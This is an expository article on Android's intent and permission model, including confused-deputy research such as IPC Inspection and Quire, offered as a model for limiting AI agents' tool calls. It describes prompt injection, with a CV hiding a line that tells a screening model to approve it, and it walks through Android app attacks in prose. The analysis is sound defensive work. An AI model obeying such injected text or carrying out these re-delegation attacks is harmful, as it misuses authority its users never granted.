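# Android's intent and permission model as a way to limit what AI agents may call

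## What apps, AI agents and permissions are

Android is Google's operating system for phones and tablets. A phone usually carries many apps, written by developers who have no particular reason to trust one another, so Android keeps the apps apart. It gives each app its own user ID and runs it in its own process. The Android Open Source Project's *Application Sandbox* explains that, by default, apps cannot interact with each other and can reach only a limited part of the system. If an app tries to read another app's data, or to dial the phone without permission, Android blocks it.

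A phone would be fairly useless if its apps were completely isolated, because a messaging app needs the camera and a restaurant guide needs to open a map. Android therefore lets apps call each other but controls those calls. An app sends an addressed message called an intent. The receiving app has declared which of its parts other apps may reach, and the system checks that the caller holds any permission the receiver requires.

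AI agents seem to raise a similar problem. An agent is a program in which a language model, the kind of AI behind ChatGPT or Gemini, chooses which tools to call, in what order and with what arguments. The tools may read mail, spend money or delete files, and some give access to other agents with their own tools. Someone has to limit what an agent may call, and Android's way of limiting what apps may call is an obvious candidate.

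### Who may do what

In the simplest form of access control, someone asks to perform an operation on an object, and a trusted program allows or refuses the request. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) uses "principal" for the party that holds rights and is accountable for their use. Its first part, *Basic Principles of Information Protection*, describes an imaginary wall around every object worth protecting, with a door and a guard at the door.

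In one of their examples, an airline lets a booking clerk make and cancel reservations for passengers whose names the clerk can supply. A gate clerk can also print the full passenger list for a flight. The airline may want to keep that list from the booking clerk so that a police request for it goes to the right manager. If the booking clerk tries to print the list, the clerk is the principal, printing is the operation, the list is the object, and the reservation program is the guard that refuses the request.

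Saltzer and Schroeder want the system to check every access to every object, because a check that people can bypass is of little use. They also want the system to deny access by default. A mistake in the rules then tends to lock out someone who will complain, whereas a mistake in a system that allows access by default tends to let someone in, and nobody may notice for years.

On Android, the app is the principal, the operating system is the guard, and the objects include the camera, the phone's location and its text messages. Each app ships with a file called a manifest, in which its author lists the named rights, or permissions, that the app needs.

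Under the principle of least privilege, a program should have only the permissions its job requires. A flashlight app needs only the lamp next to the camera. If it can also read the address book and use the network, a bug or a dishonest developer can send the address book to a stranger. Without those permissions, the worst the same bug can do is stop the lamp from working. Real flashlight apps have been notorious for requesting far more than the lamp. Saltzer and Schroeder point out that least privilege also leaves investigators with fewer programs to examine when somebody misuses a permission.

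The guard also needs a way to tell who may pass, either a list of names or tickets. A capability is a ticket that nobody can forge and that is enough to prove its holder may use the object it names. A password-reset link is a familiar example. Tennison's *Good Practices for Capability URLs* explains that anyone who opens such a link before it expires can change the account's password. The site doesn't check who they are, because the link both identifies the account and carries the right to reset its password.

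Tickets are easy to pass on, which is a large part of their appeal and also their main problem. A document's owner can give a colleague limited access by sending a link that permits viewing and keeping the one that permits editing. But links also end up in browser histories and server logs, and Tennison notes that cancelling a leaked link cuts off everyone using it, unless the site gave each person a separate link.

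The case for capabilities rests largely on a failure called the confused deputy. The name comes from a story that Hardy calls nearly true in *The Confused Deputy*. Tymshare, which sold time on shared computers, offered its customers a compiler, a program that translates source code into a form the machine can run. Customers could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. The compiler also kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so Tymshare had given it permission to write to any file there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. When one customer named the billing file as the destination for the debugging output, the operating system checked that the compiler had permission to write in that directory and let it overwrite the bills.

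Every check in this story worked as designed. The customer had no right to access the billing file, but the request came from the compiler, which had that right for a different purpose. Hardy attributes the failure to the compiler having two sources of authority, the customer and the licence, and no way to tell the system which one it was using for a given write. Tymshare first added a command for switching between the two, but soon found programs that needed more than two. With capabilities, the customer would give the compiler a ticket for the output file instead of typing a name, and could not direct it to write to the billing file without a ticket for that file, which the customer doesn't have.

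A common version of this problem occurs on the web when a malicious page makes a visitor's browser send a request to the visitor's bank. The browser automatically attaches the login cookie, so the request looks as if the customer sent it.

### How an agent works

A language model by itself only produces text. Granados (2026), in *MCP 2026 changes the rules*, describes what this is like in practice: the model suggests a list of steps, and the user becomes its hands, opening the calendar and sending the email. Tools let software do that part. Suppose a user asks an assistant to find the noodle recipe in Lisa's email and add the ingredients to a shopping list, a request that appears in Android Developers' *Overview of AppFunctions*, part of Google's documentation for app programmers. An agent would handle it in a loop:

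1. The program around the model sends it the user's request, together with descriptions of the available tools.
2. The model replies with a request for a tool call. Here it names the email search tool and supplies a search term such as "Lisa noodle recipe".
3. The program runs the tool and adds the result, the text of Lisa's email, to the conversation.
4. The model receives the conversation again, now with the email in it, and requests the next call, which adds noodles and the rest to the shopping list.

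The cycle continues until the model replies without requesting a tool. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, documents this loop for its agent toolkit, and GitHub's *The agent loop* describes nearly the same loop for its Copilot coding assistant.

In this arrangement, the model writes out the name of a tool and some arguments, and ordinary software opens the mailbox. Developers can therefore put a check between the request and the action. Anthropic's toolkit, for example, lets them insert code that inspects, changes or blocks a call before it runs.

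The model also receives the whole conversation at each turn, according to GitHub, including all earlier tool results, so Lisa's email sits in the same text as the user's request. This allows prompt injection, where a model follows text in a document, web page or tool result as if it were an instruction from its user. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the screening model to approve the application.

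Current models enforce no boundary between instructions and data, so David C proposes thinking of a model as an "inherently confusable deputy". Like Tymshare's compiler, a model can use rights that the attacker lacks. Programmers could fix the compiler, but David C doubts that anyone can fully fix the model and advises designers to limit the damage instead.

### Tools and the Model Context Protocol

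Anthropic introduced the Model Context Protocol (MCP) in 2024 as a common way to connect AI applications with outside systems. An MCP server is a program that offers tools through this protocol, and it may run on the user's machine or remotely. The application the user interacts with is the host, which creates a separate client for each server it connects to. Under MCP's design, a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into other servers, and the host is responsible for enforcing security policy and consent.

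The protocol is in wide use. With the release of the July 2026 version, the Model Context Protocol (2026) project reported close to half a billion downloads a month of its main developer kits. (Automated systems download such kits over and over, so the number of people involved must be far smaller.)

The client asks the server for a list of tools, and the server returns an entry for each. In an example from the specification, Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the entry for a weather tool consists mainly of the name `get_weather`, a sentence saying that the tool gets current weather information for a location, and a schema. The schema formally defines the tool's arguments, in this case one piece of text holding a city name or zip code. To use the tool, the client sends its name and a value such as "New York", and the server returns the temperature. The model chooses between tools by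 reading these descriptions.

The specification calls tools "model-controlled", meaning that the model can discover and invoke them based on its own reading of the conversation. It recommends, but does not require, that a human always be able to deny a call. Servers must implement access controls, and they can limit the tools a caller sees to those its authorization covers. The list may also change over time.

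The older ideas carry over to the Model Context Protocol. For example, a shop's server might create a shopping basket and return an identifier, which the model repeats in each later call. If the server knows who its callers are, the identifier is, in the protocol's words, "a name, not a capability", and the server should check on every call that the caller may use that basket. On a server without logins, anyone who has the identifier can use the basket, as with the password-reset link, so the specification advises making the identifier hard to guess and limiting how long it works.

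In a multi-agent system, several agents divide a task among themselves. The assistant with the noodle recipe might send the ingredients to a second agent, run by a supermarket. The assistant can use this agent like any other tool, by sending a request and receiving an answer. The supermarket's agent picks the products and calls a payment tool on behalf of a user who has dealt only with the assistant.

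### Two meanings of "intent"

On Android, an intent is a piece of data. Android Developers defines it as "a messaging object you can use to request an action" from a component, which is one of an app's entry points. The Android Open Source Project's *App security* gives the example of an app that needs to display a web page. The app creates an intent to view the page's address and hands it to the system, which finds and runs a browser that can handle it.

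In ordinary English an intent is a purpose, and Google's documentation also uses the word this way. The Android Developers site, for example, describes agents calling app functions to "fulfill user intents", meaning the things users want done. Someone who taps "share" under a holiday photo may want only a sister to see it. The resulting message object contains an action (send), a type of data and the photo, but it need not include anything about the sister or about who else should never get the picture. Here, "intent" refers to Android's message object, and "the user's goal" refers to what a person wants.

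### Code written in advance, calls chosen during the task

An Android app comes as a single file that its developer has signed and that includes the manifest. Before anyone installed the app, the developer decided where the code would use the camera or send an intent. The user's taps and the incoming data determine which of those points the app reaches and with what values, but a patient reviewer could in principle find the points by reading the code.

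A reviewer reading an agent's code would find a loop that runs whatever tool the model selects. The developers also wrote this loop in advance, but the choice of the next tool depends on the user's request, the tool descriptions and the results so far. The same agent may therefore use the same tools to search a mailbox in one task and empty it in another.

Google's Android Developers site describes AppFunctions, which let apps on Android 16 and later offer functions to agents, as "the mobile equivalent of tools within the Model Context Protocol" (MCP). A caller needs an Android permission to use them, and the agent then picks the function and its parameters based on the user's prompt. Android and MCP are also similar in structure. MCP servers, like apps, come from many authors, and each server publishes a list of what it offers. A host stands between the model and the servers, roughly where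 Android stands between one app and the next.

Android's checks rely on assumptions about callers and users that made sense for apps. It is an open question how many of these assumptions still hold when the caller is an agent. It is also unclear whether checking if a program may make a particular call can usefully limit a program that works out its calls during the task, either alone or through other agents.

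## How Android decides which app may call which

Suppose a phone has three apps: a notes app, a calendar from the same developer, and a game from another developer. The notes app has one screen for locked notes, which no other app should open, and another where any app may send text to be saved. It also runs a background service that lets the calendar copy notes containing dates. The developer of the notes app wants the game to be able to save text but do nothing else with the notes app.

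Android offers a handful of settings for this. They are easiest to understand in the order in which a call runs into them.

### A user ID for each app

On a desktop computer, a program usually runs with all the rights of the person who started it. Ransomware often needs no security hole there, because it can rewrite every file the user can edit. *The Android Platform Security Model* (2019), by Mayrhofer, Vander Stoep and colleagues at Google, describes how the company broke with this design by not treating Android apps as "fully authorized agents for user actions".

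Linux, the system at Android's core, uses numeric user IDs to separate people who share a computer. Android assigns these IDs to apps instead, using the numbers from 10000 to 19999. If several people share the device, each additional person's apps get the same range shifted by a multiple of 100,000. When an app requests the phone's position, the location service checks whether that app's ID has the location permission. The kernel, the innermost part of the operating system, keeps the apps' processes apart, so the separation doesn't depend on which programming language the developer used.

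Google's *9.2. UID and Process Isolation*, part of the rules for device makers, requires phones to support running several apps under one user ID if their developer has signed them properly. The kernel treats such apps as a single principal. The notes app and the calendar in this example have separate IDs, as apps normally do.

### How the receiver learns who is calling

Apps in separate processes cannot call each other's functions directly, so Android carries the calls through a part of the kernel named Binder. In Google's *Binder overview*, a call goes roughly like this:

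1. Code in the calling app packs up an identifier for the object it wants to reach, an identifier for the function, and copies of the arguments.
2. It hands the package to the Binder driver in the kernel, which works out which process hosts the object.
3. The kernel copies the package into that process and finds a thread there to handle it.
4. The thread unpacks the arguments and runs the function, and the result travels back the same way.

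The kernel also attaches the caller's user ID to each call, and the caller cannot choose that ID. Horn (2026), in *[PATCH 1/2] binder*, proposed a one-line change to the kernel code that sets the ID, so that it would come from the task making the call instead of the process that originally opened the connection to Binder.

The receiving code can use this ID to look up the calling app and the certificate its developer signed it with. Chromium's *Android IPC Security Considerations*, a guide for people who work on Chrome's underlying code, describes this as the only reliable way for one app to authenticate another.

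Intents also travel over Binder, but the sender passes the intent to a system process, which passes it to the receiver. The system can therefore identify the sender and check its permissions, while the receiver usually can't. The Chromium project calls it "fundamentally impossible" to determine an intent's sender, except when the sender started a screen and asked for a result. The notes app therefore has to tell the system in advance, in its manifest, which senders to reject.

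### Explicit and implicit intents

An intent can contain the name of a component, an action such as "view" or "send", the address or type of data, and categories that describe the kind of component wanted. It can also carry extras, which are named values such as the text of a message or the subject of an email.

An explicit intent names its receiver. The notes app uses one to open its own locked screen, since the developer knows the name of that screen's code. An implicit intent describes the job instead, and Android has to find a receiver. For example, if a player wants to share a high score, the game can create an intent with the action "send", the data type `text/plain`, and the score as an extra.

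It does so by comparing the intent with the intent filters in the manifests of the installed apps. A filter is a component's declaration of the implicit intents it can handle. Android Developers sets out three tests, and the intent must pass all of them:

- The filter must list the intent's action. An intent without an action passes as long as the filter lists at least one.
- The filter must list every category in the intent, though it may list others as well. Android adds a category named `DEFAULT` to every implicit intent that opens a screen, so a screen whose filter leaves out `DEFAULT` never receives any.
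- The data must fit. A filter for `image/*` accepts any type of image. Where a filter specifies a web address, Android compares only the parts that the filter mentions, so a filter with a site's name and no path accepts every page on that site.

The data test has a small exception. A filter that lists only a data type also accepts data held on the phone, in a file or in another app, even though the filter lists no address for it. Most data that apps share comes from these sources, so without this exception developers would have to add the same lines to nearly every filter.

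If one component passes, Android opens it immediately. If none does, the sender gets an error. If several pass, the user picks one from a dialog and can make it the default. A default suits web pages, since most people use the same browser every time. For sharing, Android Developers recommends a version of the dialog that does not allow a default, because someone may want to email one photo and post the next.

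None of the three tests checks whether the receiving app can be trusted. Developers write the filters that describe what their own components can do, and the game's developer could declare a filter for shared text as easily as anyone else. Chromium warns that an implicit intent can deliver a user's data to an unexpected and possibly malicious app, and recommends explicit intents whenever the sender can know the receiver. The risk is greater with services because they have no screen, so the user can't see which one has started.

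### Exported components and required permissions

An intent filter helps Android find a component to receive an intent. An explicit intent already names its receiver, so a filter that accepts only text doesn't stop another app from sending the component something else. Android Developers warns that another app may be able to start a component with an explicit intent if that app's developer finds out the component's name. Anyone can find the name by unpacking the app that contains the component.

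The lock is a separate setting, `android:exported`. If it is `false`, other apps cannot start the component at all. If it is `true`, they can, subject to any permission that the component requires from its callers. The notes app's manifest would contain these lines:

```xml
<permission
    android:name="com.example.notes.permission.SYNC"
    android:protectionLevel="signature" />

<application>
    <activity
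        android:name=".LockedNotesActivity"
        android:exported="false" />

    <activity
        android:name=".AddNoteActivity"
        android:exported="true">
        <intent-filter>
            <data android:mimeType="text/plain" />
            <category android:name="android.intent.category.DEFAULT" />
            <action android:name="android.intent.action.SEND" />
        </intent-filter>
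    </activity>

    <service
        android:name=".SyncService"
        android:exported="true"
        android:permission="com.example.notes.permission.SYNC" />
</application>
```

Android calls a screen an "activity". The filter on the second screen closely resembles a sample in Google's *Let other apps start your activity*, though the sample also accepts images. Apps can define their own permissions as well as use Android's, and the first few lines define a new one. The word `signature` means Android grants this permission only to apps signed with the same certificate as the notes app.

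The calendar needs a line in its own manifest to request the permission:

```xml
<uses-permission android:name="com.example.notes.permission.SYNC" />
```

The three apps can then reach the following:

| Component | Notes app itself | Calendar (same certificate, requests `SYNC`) | Game (another developer) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Locked notes screen | Yes | No | No |
| Add-note screen | Yes | Yes | Yes |
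| Sync service | Yes | Yes | No |

The calendar can't open the locked notes, even though the same person wrote both apps, because `exported="false"` keeps out every other app. The game's developer could add the same request for `SYNC` to the game's manifest, but Android would not grant it, and no user could override that. The developer also couldn't get around this by declaring a second permission with the same name. According to Google's reference for the `permission` element, Android won't install an app that reuses an existing permission's name unless the same certificate signed both apps.

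The game can still send the add-note screen any data that fits in an intent, and nothing in the manifest restricts that data. Any app can also send Chrome an intent, so the Chromium project tells its programmers never to fully trust the contents and to validate them before passing them to other parts of the browser.

A permission in the manifest also covers the whole component. If the sync service has one function for reading notes and another for deleting them, the calendar can call both. To separate them, the developer has to write a check inside the service. Google documents a function, `getCallingUid()`, that returns the ID Binder attached to the current call. The delete function can use it to refuse every ID except the notes app's. Android's location service works in a similar way.

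A related function, `clearCallingIdentity()`, lets a service set aside the caller's ID and continue under its own. Services need this when they do work that the caller isn't entitled to do directly. If a developer clears the ID before checking permissions, the check will apply to the service's rights instead of the caller's, which is the same kind of flaw that Tymshare's compiler had.

### Protection levels

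Whoever declares a permission also chooses its protection level, which determines how other apps can get it. Google's reference lists a few basic types, to which developers can add flags. Mayrhofer and colleagues add a class, special access, for permissions so risky that an app may not show a dialog asking for them.

| Level | How an app gets the permission | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Normal | Android grants it at installation without asking anyone | Using the internet |
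| Dangerous | The user approves it in a dialog | Location, camera |
| Special access | The user finds the right page in the phone's settings and switches it on | Reading all notifications |
| Signature | Android grants it if the app has the same certificate as the declarer | Configuring network interfaces |
| Known signer | Android grants it if the app's certificate is on the declarer's list | A partner company's app |
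| Signature or privileged | As for signature, but the device maker can also approve preinstalled apps by name | Privileged use of Bluetooth |
| Role | Android grants it to the app that holds a certain job on the phone | The default app for text messages |

Only some of these involve the user. Developers, device makers and Google decide the rest before the user opens the app. Mayrhofer and colleagues present this as part of a general rule that the user, the developer and the platform must all consent to an action. Even a user who wants the game to read the locked notes therefore cannot allow it. Mayrhofer and colleagues see this as a benefit because nobody can trick the user into allowing it either.

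Each permission has a protection level that doesn't depend on why an app requests it. Android therefore uses the same procedure for a location request from a weather app as for one from a stalking app.

### Access to one item: URI grants

The permissions described so far cover whole components or whole kinds of data, which is more access than many ordinary requests need. Suppose a user wants to send a friend a photo from a note through a messaging app. The messaging app needs that photo but should not see the rest of the notes.

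An Android app can share a single item with another app through a URI grant. To share a photo with a messaging app, for example, a notes app puts the photo's address (its URI, such as `content://com.example.notes/photos/17`) in an intent and adds a flag that permits reading. Android then temporarily allows the messaging app to read the item at that address. Mayrhofer and colleagues count four acts of consent in this kind of sharing: the user chooses the messaging app, the notes app offers the photo, the messaging app accepts it, and the platform ensures that the messaging app gets only that photo.

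A URI grant resembles a capability, since it gives access to one object and the app that controls the object can hand it out. Unlike a password-reset link, it works for only one recipient, because Android records the grant under the receiving app's ID. An app that has only seen the URI can't use it to access the object.

Before this became the norm, some developers shared files by making them readable to every app on the phone. The Android Open Source Project says that practice led to leaks and confused-deputy vulnerabilities, and Android 9 blocked it for apps written for that version or later.

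When an app shares an item using the standard "send" action, Android automatically gives the receiving app a URI grant to both read and write the item, even if the sender didn't want it edited. According to Google's *Behavior changes* for Android 17, Google plans to change this in Android 18 and wants senders to specify the permissions themselves.

### Acting as another app: PendingIntent

Suppose the notes app posts a reminder notification, and tapping it should open a locked note. The notes app may not be running when the user taps. A system process displays the notification and has to open the note's screen, but that screen belongs to the notes app and isn't exported.

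The notes app solves this by creating a PendingIntent, a wrapper around an intent. Whoever holds the wrapper can send the intent inside it, and Android treats the intent as if the notes app had sent it. Home-screen widgets and alarms work the same way. An app can also give a PendingIntent to another ordinary app. If the notes app gave the game one that opens the locked notes, the game could open them, despite the "No" in the table.

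Chromium compares the PendingIntent to a setuid program, a Unix program that runs with its owner's rights no matter who starts it. A PendingIntent is the closest thing to a true capability in everyday Android programming. The kernel backs the token inside it, so nobody can forge one, and its holder can pass it on. The receiver can find out which app created the PendingIntent, but nobody can find out which app finally used it. Chromium therefore advises programmers to use such tokens to control access and never to identify the caller, because an app may have passed its token on deliberately, by accident or because of a bug.

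The power a PendingIntent gives its holder depends on how much of the intent its creator has filled in. A notification with a reply box, for instance, needs a PendingIntent that is partly blank, so that the system can add the user's text before sending the intent. Android calls such a PendingIntent mutable. If the creator has also left out the receiver, the holder can fill that in too, and so send an intent of its own choosing with the creator's rights.

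The holder of an immutable PendingIntent can use it but can't change it, so the notes app has handed over the right to do only one of the many things it may do on the phone. This is called attenuation, which means passing on authority that can only be narrower than the giver's own. It becomes important when one program delegates work to another.

### How the rules tightened

Google used to leave many of these choices to developers, who often made them without noticing. For example, a component with an intent filter and no `exported` setting was open to other apps by default, so a developer who added a filter for internal use could expose the component to every app on the phone.

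Android 12 ended this. According to Google's *Behavior changes* for that version, an app that targets Android 12 must state whether each component with a filter is exported, or the phone won't install it. An app "targets" a version when its developer declares that it is ready for that version's rules. Most newer restrictions apply only to apps that target the relevant version, so older apps still work but keep their weaknesses.

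| Android version | Change |
|---|---|
| 5.0 | Apps can no longer connect to a service with an implicit intent |
| 6.0 | Developers can make a PendingIntent immutable |
| 12 | Components with filters must declare whether they are exported; developers must mark each PendingIntent as mutable or immutable; a debugging tool warns of unsafe launches of nested intents |
| 13 | Intents from other apps must match a filter, if the receiving component has any |
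| 14 | Implicit intents reach only exported components; a mutable PendingIntent must name a receiving app or component |
| 16 | Protection against redirected intents is on by default; developers can switch on stricter matching |
| 17 | Limits on opening screens from the background extend to a further way of sending intents |

Under Android 14, an app can no longer use an implicit intent to reach its own internal components, such as a screen. Developers now have to name the component. Google explains that the rule protects the sender, because a malicious app could declare a filter that matched the implicit intent and intercept the request.

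The nested intents in the table are intents carried inside another intent's extras. Some apps take out the inner intent and launch it under their own ID. If the notes app did this with any intent that reached its add-note screen, the game could send it an inner intent addressed to the locked notes, and the notes app would open them. Google calls this intent redirection, and Android 16 introduced a default defence for every app, whatever version the app targets. Developers can remove the protection from a particular intent if it causes problems. They can also screen inner intents themselves with a tool, described in Google's *Intent redirection*, that accepts only the components, addresses and data types on a list.

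It is unclear how far Android now requires explicit intents to match a component's filters, because Google's two accounts are hard to reconcile. Android Developers states that if an app targets Android 13 or later, intents from other apps reach an exported component only if they match the actions and categories of one of its filters. But Google describes similar matching for explicit intents as new in Android 16, and expects it to have limited effect at first because developers have to turn it on in the manifest. A careful developer would assume that an explicit intent can still reach any exported component, and would use the export setting and a permission to keep callers out.

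Google was still working on these problems in Android 17. Its *Behavior changes* for apps targeting that version gives confused-deputy attacks as one reason for the new limits on opening screens.

### Six assumptions

All these checks rely on assumptions about apps and their users that are only roughly true, even on a phone, but hold well enough for the checks to be useful.

1. The developer fixes the caller's code before it runs, so a reviewer can compare it with the permissions it requests. Google has been trying to make this assumption truer. Since Android 14, apps that target that version must mark certain code files as read-only if they load them while running, and Android 17 extends the rule to libraries of native code. An app can still take orders from its developer's server, but only orders that its code already knows how to carry out.

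2. The caller's identity shows whose authority the call uses. When a call arrives with the calendar's ID, Android applies the calendar's permissions and never considers who put the calendar up to it. A PendingIntent separates the two on purpose, and intent redirection separates them by mistake.

3. Data in a message does not command the receiver. The add-note screen saves the text that the game sends, even if the text happens to be "delete all notes". An app that launches nested intents does let a message direct it, but that is a bug in a particular piece of code, and its developer can fix it.

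4. A permission names an operation with known consequences. Google could rate camera access as dangerous and internet access as normal, for all apps at once, because each permission allows much the same thing in any app. The notes app's developer could likewise choose a level for `SYNC` because the developer had written the service behind it.

5. Checking each call separately is enough. Android checks one permission when an app reads the address book and another when it opens an internet connection. Some permissions apply only while the app is on screen, so the checks do take some account of circumstances. But they take none of what the app has just read, and an app that holds both permissions can send the address book anywhere.

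6. A user can judge requests. Android depends on this whenever it shows a permission dialog or a list of apps to share with. Mayrhofer and colleagues consider meaningful consent from users by far the hardest kind to obtain. They recommend asking rarely, and letting people pick a single contact instead of asking them to open up the whole address book.

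## How Android apps came to use permissions they did not hold

On phones running Android 2.2, released in 2010, an app with no permissions could switch on the GPS by sending an intent to the phone's Settings app. Settings had permission to control the GPS and switched it on in response.

Felt, Wang and colleagues (2011) named this failure in *Permission Re-Delegation*. Permission re-delegation happens when an app that holds a permission performs a protected operation for an app that doesn't, without involving the user. It is a confused deputy problem in which the user granted the deputy's permission. Wei and Xiong (2026), in *Access Control for Agentic AI*, cite it as an early case of a problem they now see when AI agents delegate to one another.

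### The attack on Settings

The Settings app has buttons for Wi-Fi, Bluetooth and GPS. When the user pressed one, the screen sent an intent to another part of the same app, a broadcast receiver, which is a component that runs in the background when a message arrives. The receiver then changed the setting. Its developer had left it open to other apps, so an attack could go like this:

1. A malicious app without the location permission sends the receiver the same intent that the Settings screen would have sent.
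2. Android delivers the intent, because the receiver is public and requires no permission from its callers.
3. The receiver asks the system to turn on the GPS.
4. Android checks whether Settings has the necessary permission. It does, so the GPS comes on.

Both apps ran code that their developers had fixed in advance, and Android made every check it was supposed to make. However, those checks wrongly relied on a caller's identity to show whose authority the call used. The malicious app had caused the last call, even though it came from Settings.

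To find out how many apps might have the same problem, Felt and colleagues collected the 16 core apps that came with Android 2.2 and 856 popular free and paid apps from Google's store. They counted an app as at risk if it held important permissions and had a service or broadcast receiver that any other app could reach. Of the 872 apps, 320 (37%) met both conditions, including 11 of the 16 core apps. An attack on these apps is conceivable but not always possible, since the component that other apps can reach may have nothing to do with the app's permissions.

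The researchers examined the core apps more closely. They used a tool that traced function calls in the disassembled code to find paths from a public component to a protected operation. They then wrote test attacks for these paths and confirmed 15 vulnerabilities in five apps. In one case, any app could make Desk Clock sound an alarm with no end time, and the phone would ring and vibrate until the user killed the clock's process. The tool couldn't follow some kinds of code, so there were probably more vulnerabilities.

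Developers could have prevented this by having their apps check callers. But of the 50 apps with public components that Felt and colleagues examined, only one checked callers in its code to protect a service or receiver. They attribute this to incentives, since an app that gives away a permission harms the user but usually not the developer. They therefore wanted a defence that would work even if developers did nothing.

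### IPC Inspection

Their answer was IPC Inspection (IPC stands for inter-process communication). When one app sends a message to another, the operating system cuts the receiver's permissions down to those that the sender also holds. If a requester *R* sends a message to a deputy *D* at time *t*, then

$$P_t(D) = P_{t-1}(D) \cap P_{t-1}(R)$$

Here $P_t(D)$ is the set of permissions that *D* holds at time *t*, and $\cap$ keeps only the permissions in both sets. The requester's own permissions stay the same.

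Suppose a messaging app may use the camera, read the location and send texts, while a photo editor may only use the camera. Once the editor sends the messaging app an intent, the messaging app is left with

$$\{\text{camera}, \text{location}, \text{texts}\} \cap \{\text{camera}\} = \{\text{camera}\}$$

The messaging app can still take a picture for the editor, but Android will block it from sending a text. The rule also applies to a chain of calls. If a game with no permissions had called the editor first, the editor would have lost its camera permission, and its call would then have left the messaging app with no permissions either.

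If the messaging app lost permissions when the editor's intent arrived, it would annoy someone who was writing a text at the time. Android therefore starts a second copy of the app to handle the intent, and only that copy loses permissions. Some apps can't run twice, such as a music player that keeps track of what is playing. Such an app loses more permissions with each intent it receives until it closes, unless it only accepts intents from apps that hold all the permissions it needs.

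Replies don't reduce any app's permissions. Felt and colleagues made this exception because of apps like Beer Cloud, which found nearby bars that served a particular beer. Beer Cloud used a separate app to scan the barcode on a bottle, then sent the result and the user's location to its server. If the scanner's reply had removed Beer Cloud's location permission, Beer Cloud would have stopped working. Because of the exception, a malicious reply can still mislead the app that requested it. For an AI agent this would be a serious gap, since a prompt injection can arrive in a tool's result.

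IPC Inspection would also break apps like Beer Cloud, which didn't need camera permission because the scanner operated the camera and asked the user first. Under the rule, the scanner would lose camera access whenever Beer Cloud called it, so Beer Cloud's developer would have to request camera permission for an app that never uses the camera itself. A file manager that sent files through Gmail would likewise need internet permission. ScrobbleDroid, which posted the songs a user had played to a website, would need four extra permissions, some of which the music player used only for other purposes.

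A rule meant to protect users would therefore push developers to request more permissions than their apps need, which least privilege is supposed to prevent. Taking the intersection also treats a careful deputy, like the scanner, the same as a careless one. Felt and colleagues suggest that Android could ask the user to grant the requester a permission for that one occasion, but they didn't build this, and it would rely on users to judge the request.

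Their prototype stopped all the attacks they had found. They looked at 20 randomly chosen apps to see how many the rule might disrupt. Eleven either offered services to other apps on purpose or used such services, so their developers might have had to make changes.

### Quire and the call chain

*Quire*, by Dietz, Shekhar and colleagues, addressed the same problem at about the same time by giving the receiver more information about where a request came from. In the paper's example, a malicious app without the location permission calls a mapping app, which then calls the phone's location service. Android normally identifies only the mapping app to the location service. Quire adds the names of the apps that led to the call, and the location service refuses it unless every app in the chain has the permission.

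The mapping app could lie about who called it, but it would gain nothing, because adding a name to the chain can only reduce what the call is allowed to do. It also can't leave itself out of the chain, because Binder gives the receiver the ID of the immediate caller.

If the deputy passes the chain along, the result is the same as taking the intersection. But a deputy can also drop the chain and make the call on its own authority. The barcode scanner could ask the user, then drop Beer Cloud from the chain and turn on the camera. The system also doesn't need second copies of apps, since the chain belongs to the request and the app keeps its permissions. An app can store the chain with a request it plans to handle later.

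The cost is that safety depends partly on developers again. Felt and colleagues point out that Quire doesn't force them to comply. A developer who drops the chain to get rid of an error message, for example, brings the original vulnerability back. Still, a developer has to do this deliberately, whereas the developer of the Settings receiver only had to overlook something. (In the prototype, developers also had to mark the functions that should carry the chain, but Dietz and colleagues say that a production version would do this automatically.)

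### Intercepted and forged intents

An intent can also reach the wrong app or come from the wrong one. Chin, Felt and colleagues studied both problems in *Analyzing Inter-Application Communication in Android* (2011).

A malicious app can intercept implicit intents by declaring a matching intent filter. Suppose a charity's app has a "Donate" button that uses an implicit intent to open a payment screen. If a malicious app's screen opens instead and looks genuine, the user may type a card number into it. The dialog for choosing between apps offers some protection, but a malicious app can give its screen a misleading name or be useful enough that the user makes it the default.

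In intent spoofing, a malicious app sends an intent to a component that is meant to receive intents only from its own app or from the system. One vulnerable app was ICE: In Case of Emergency, which let paramedics read the owner's medical details from a locked phone. Some of its receivers were meant to respond to announcements from Android, such as the one sent when the phone finishes starting up, but they didn't check that an intent contained such an announcement. Any app could therefore remove ICE from the lock screen by sending them an intent.

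To find such weaknesses, Chin and colleagues built ComDroid, a tool that follows each intent through an app's disassembled code, from where the app creates it to where the app sends it. ComDroid warns if the intent is implicit and no strong permission limits who may receive it. It also warns about components that other apps can reach without a permission, or with one that is easy to get. In 100 popular apps, it produced 1,414 warnings, 1,013 about intents and 401 about components.

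Most of these warnings were probably not serious. Chin and colleagues checked all 181 warnings for 20 randomly chosen apps by hand and found 34 vulnerabilities, 14 of which depended on tricking the user. Another 16 warnings were for bugs that weren't vulnerabilities, 25 were unclear and 106 were false alarms. Many of the false alarms were for possible attacks that would only be a nuisance, such as turning on a flashlight. But the 34 vulnerabilities were spread over 12 of the 20 apps, so a typical user probably had several vulnerable apps installed.

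Careful developers made these mistakes too. Chin and colleagues reviewed ten financial and commercial apps whose developers had clearly thought about security, and found vulnerabilities in four. The only weakness they found in how the apps handled financial information was the risk of a fake login page. The researchers concluded that the intent system itself is confusing, partly because apps used intents both internally and to communicate with other apps. iPhone apps at the time used different kinds of messages for the two purposes, so their developers were unlikely to expose a component by accident.

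They proposed that Android offer an implicit intent to the sender's own components first, and that it stop making components public just because they have an intent filter. *Improving the Security* reports that, in tests, the first change caused no trouble in one sample of apps, but the second broke some functions in another. Google made changes with similar aims in Android 12 and 14, a decade or more after the original study.

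### Collusion

In the attacks described so far, one of the two apps was an unwitting victim, but two apps can also collude. For example, one app may have permission to read the phone's location but not to use the internet, while another can use the internet but can't read the location. The first app puts the location in an intent, and the second sends it to a server. Someone who reviewed either app alone might see nothing wrong with its permissions.

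IPC Inspection wouldn't prevent this, because the first app is allowed to read the location and does so before it contacts the second. Dietz and colleagues also exclude such pairs from Quire's scope. Bugiel, Davi and colleagues (2012) addressed both confused-deputy and collusion attacks in *Towards Taming Privilege-Escalation Attacks on Android*. They added a central monitor that follows chains of calls, along with controls on files and network connections, and tested it against known attacks of both kinds.

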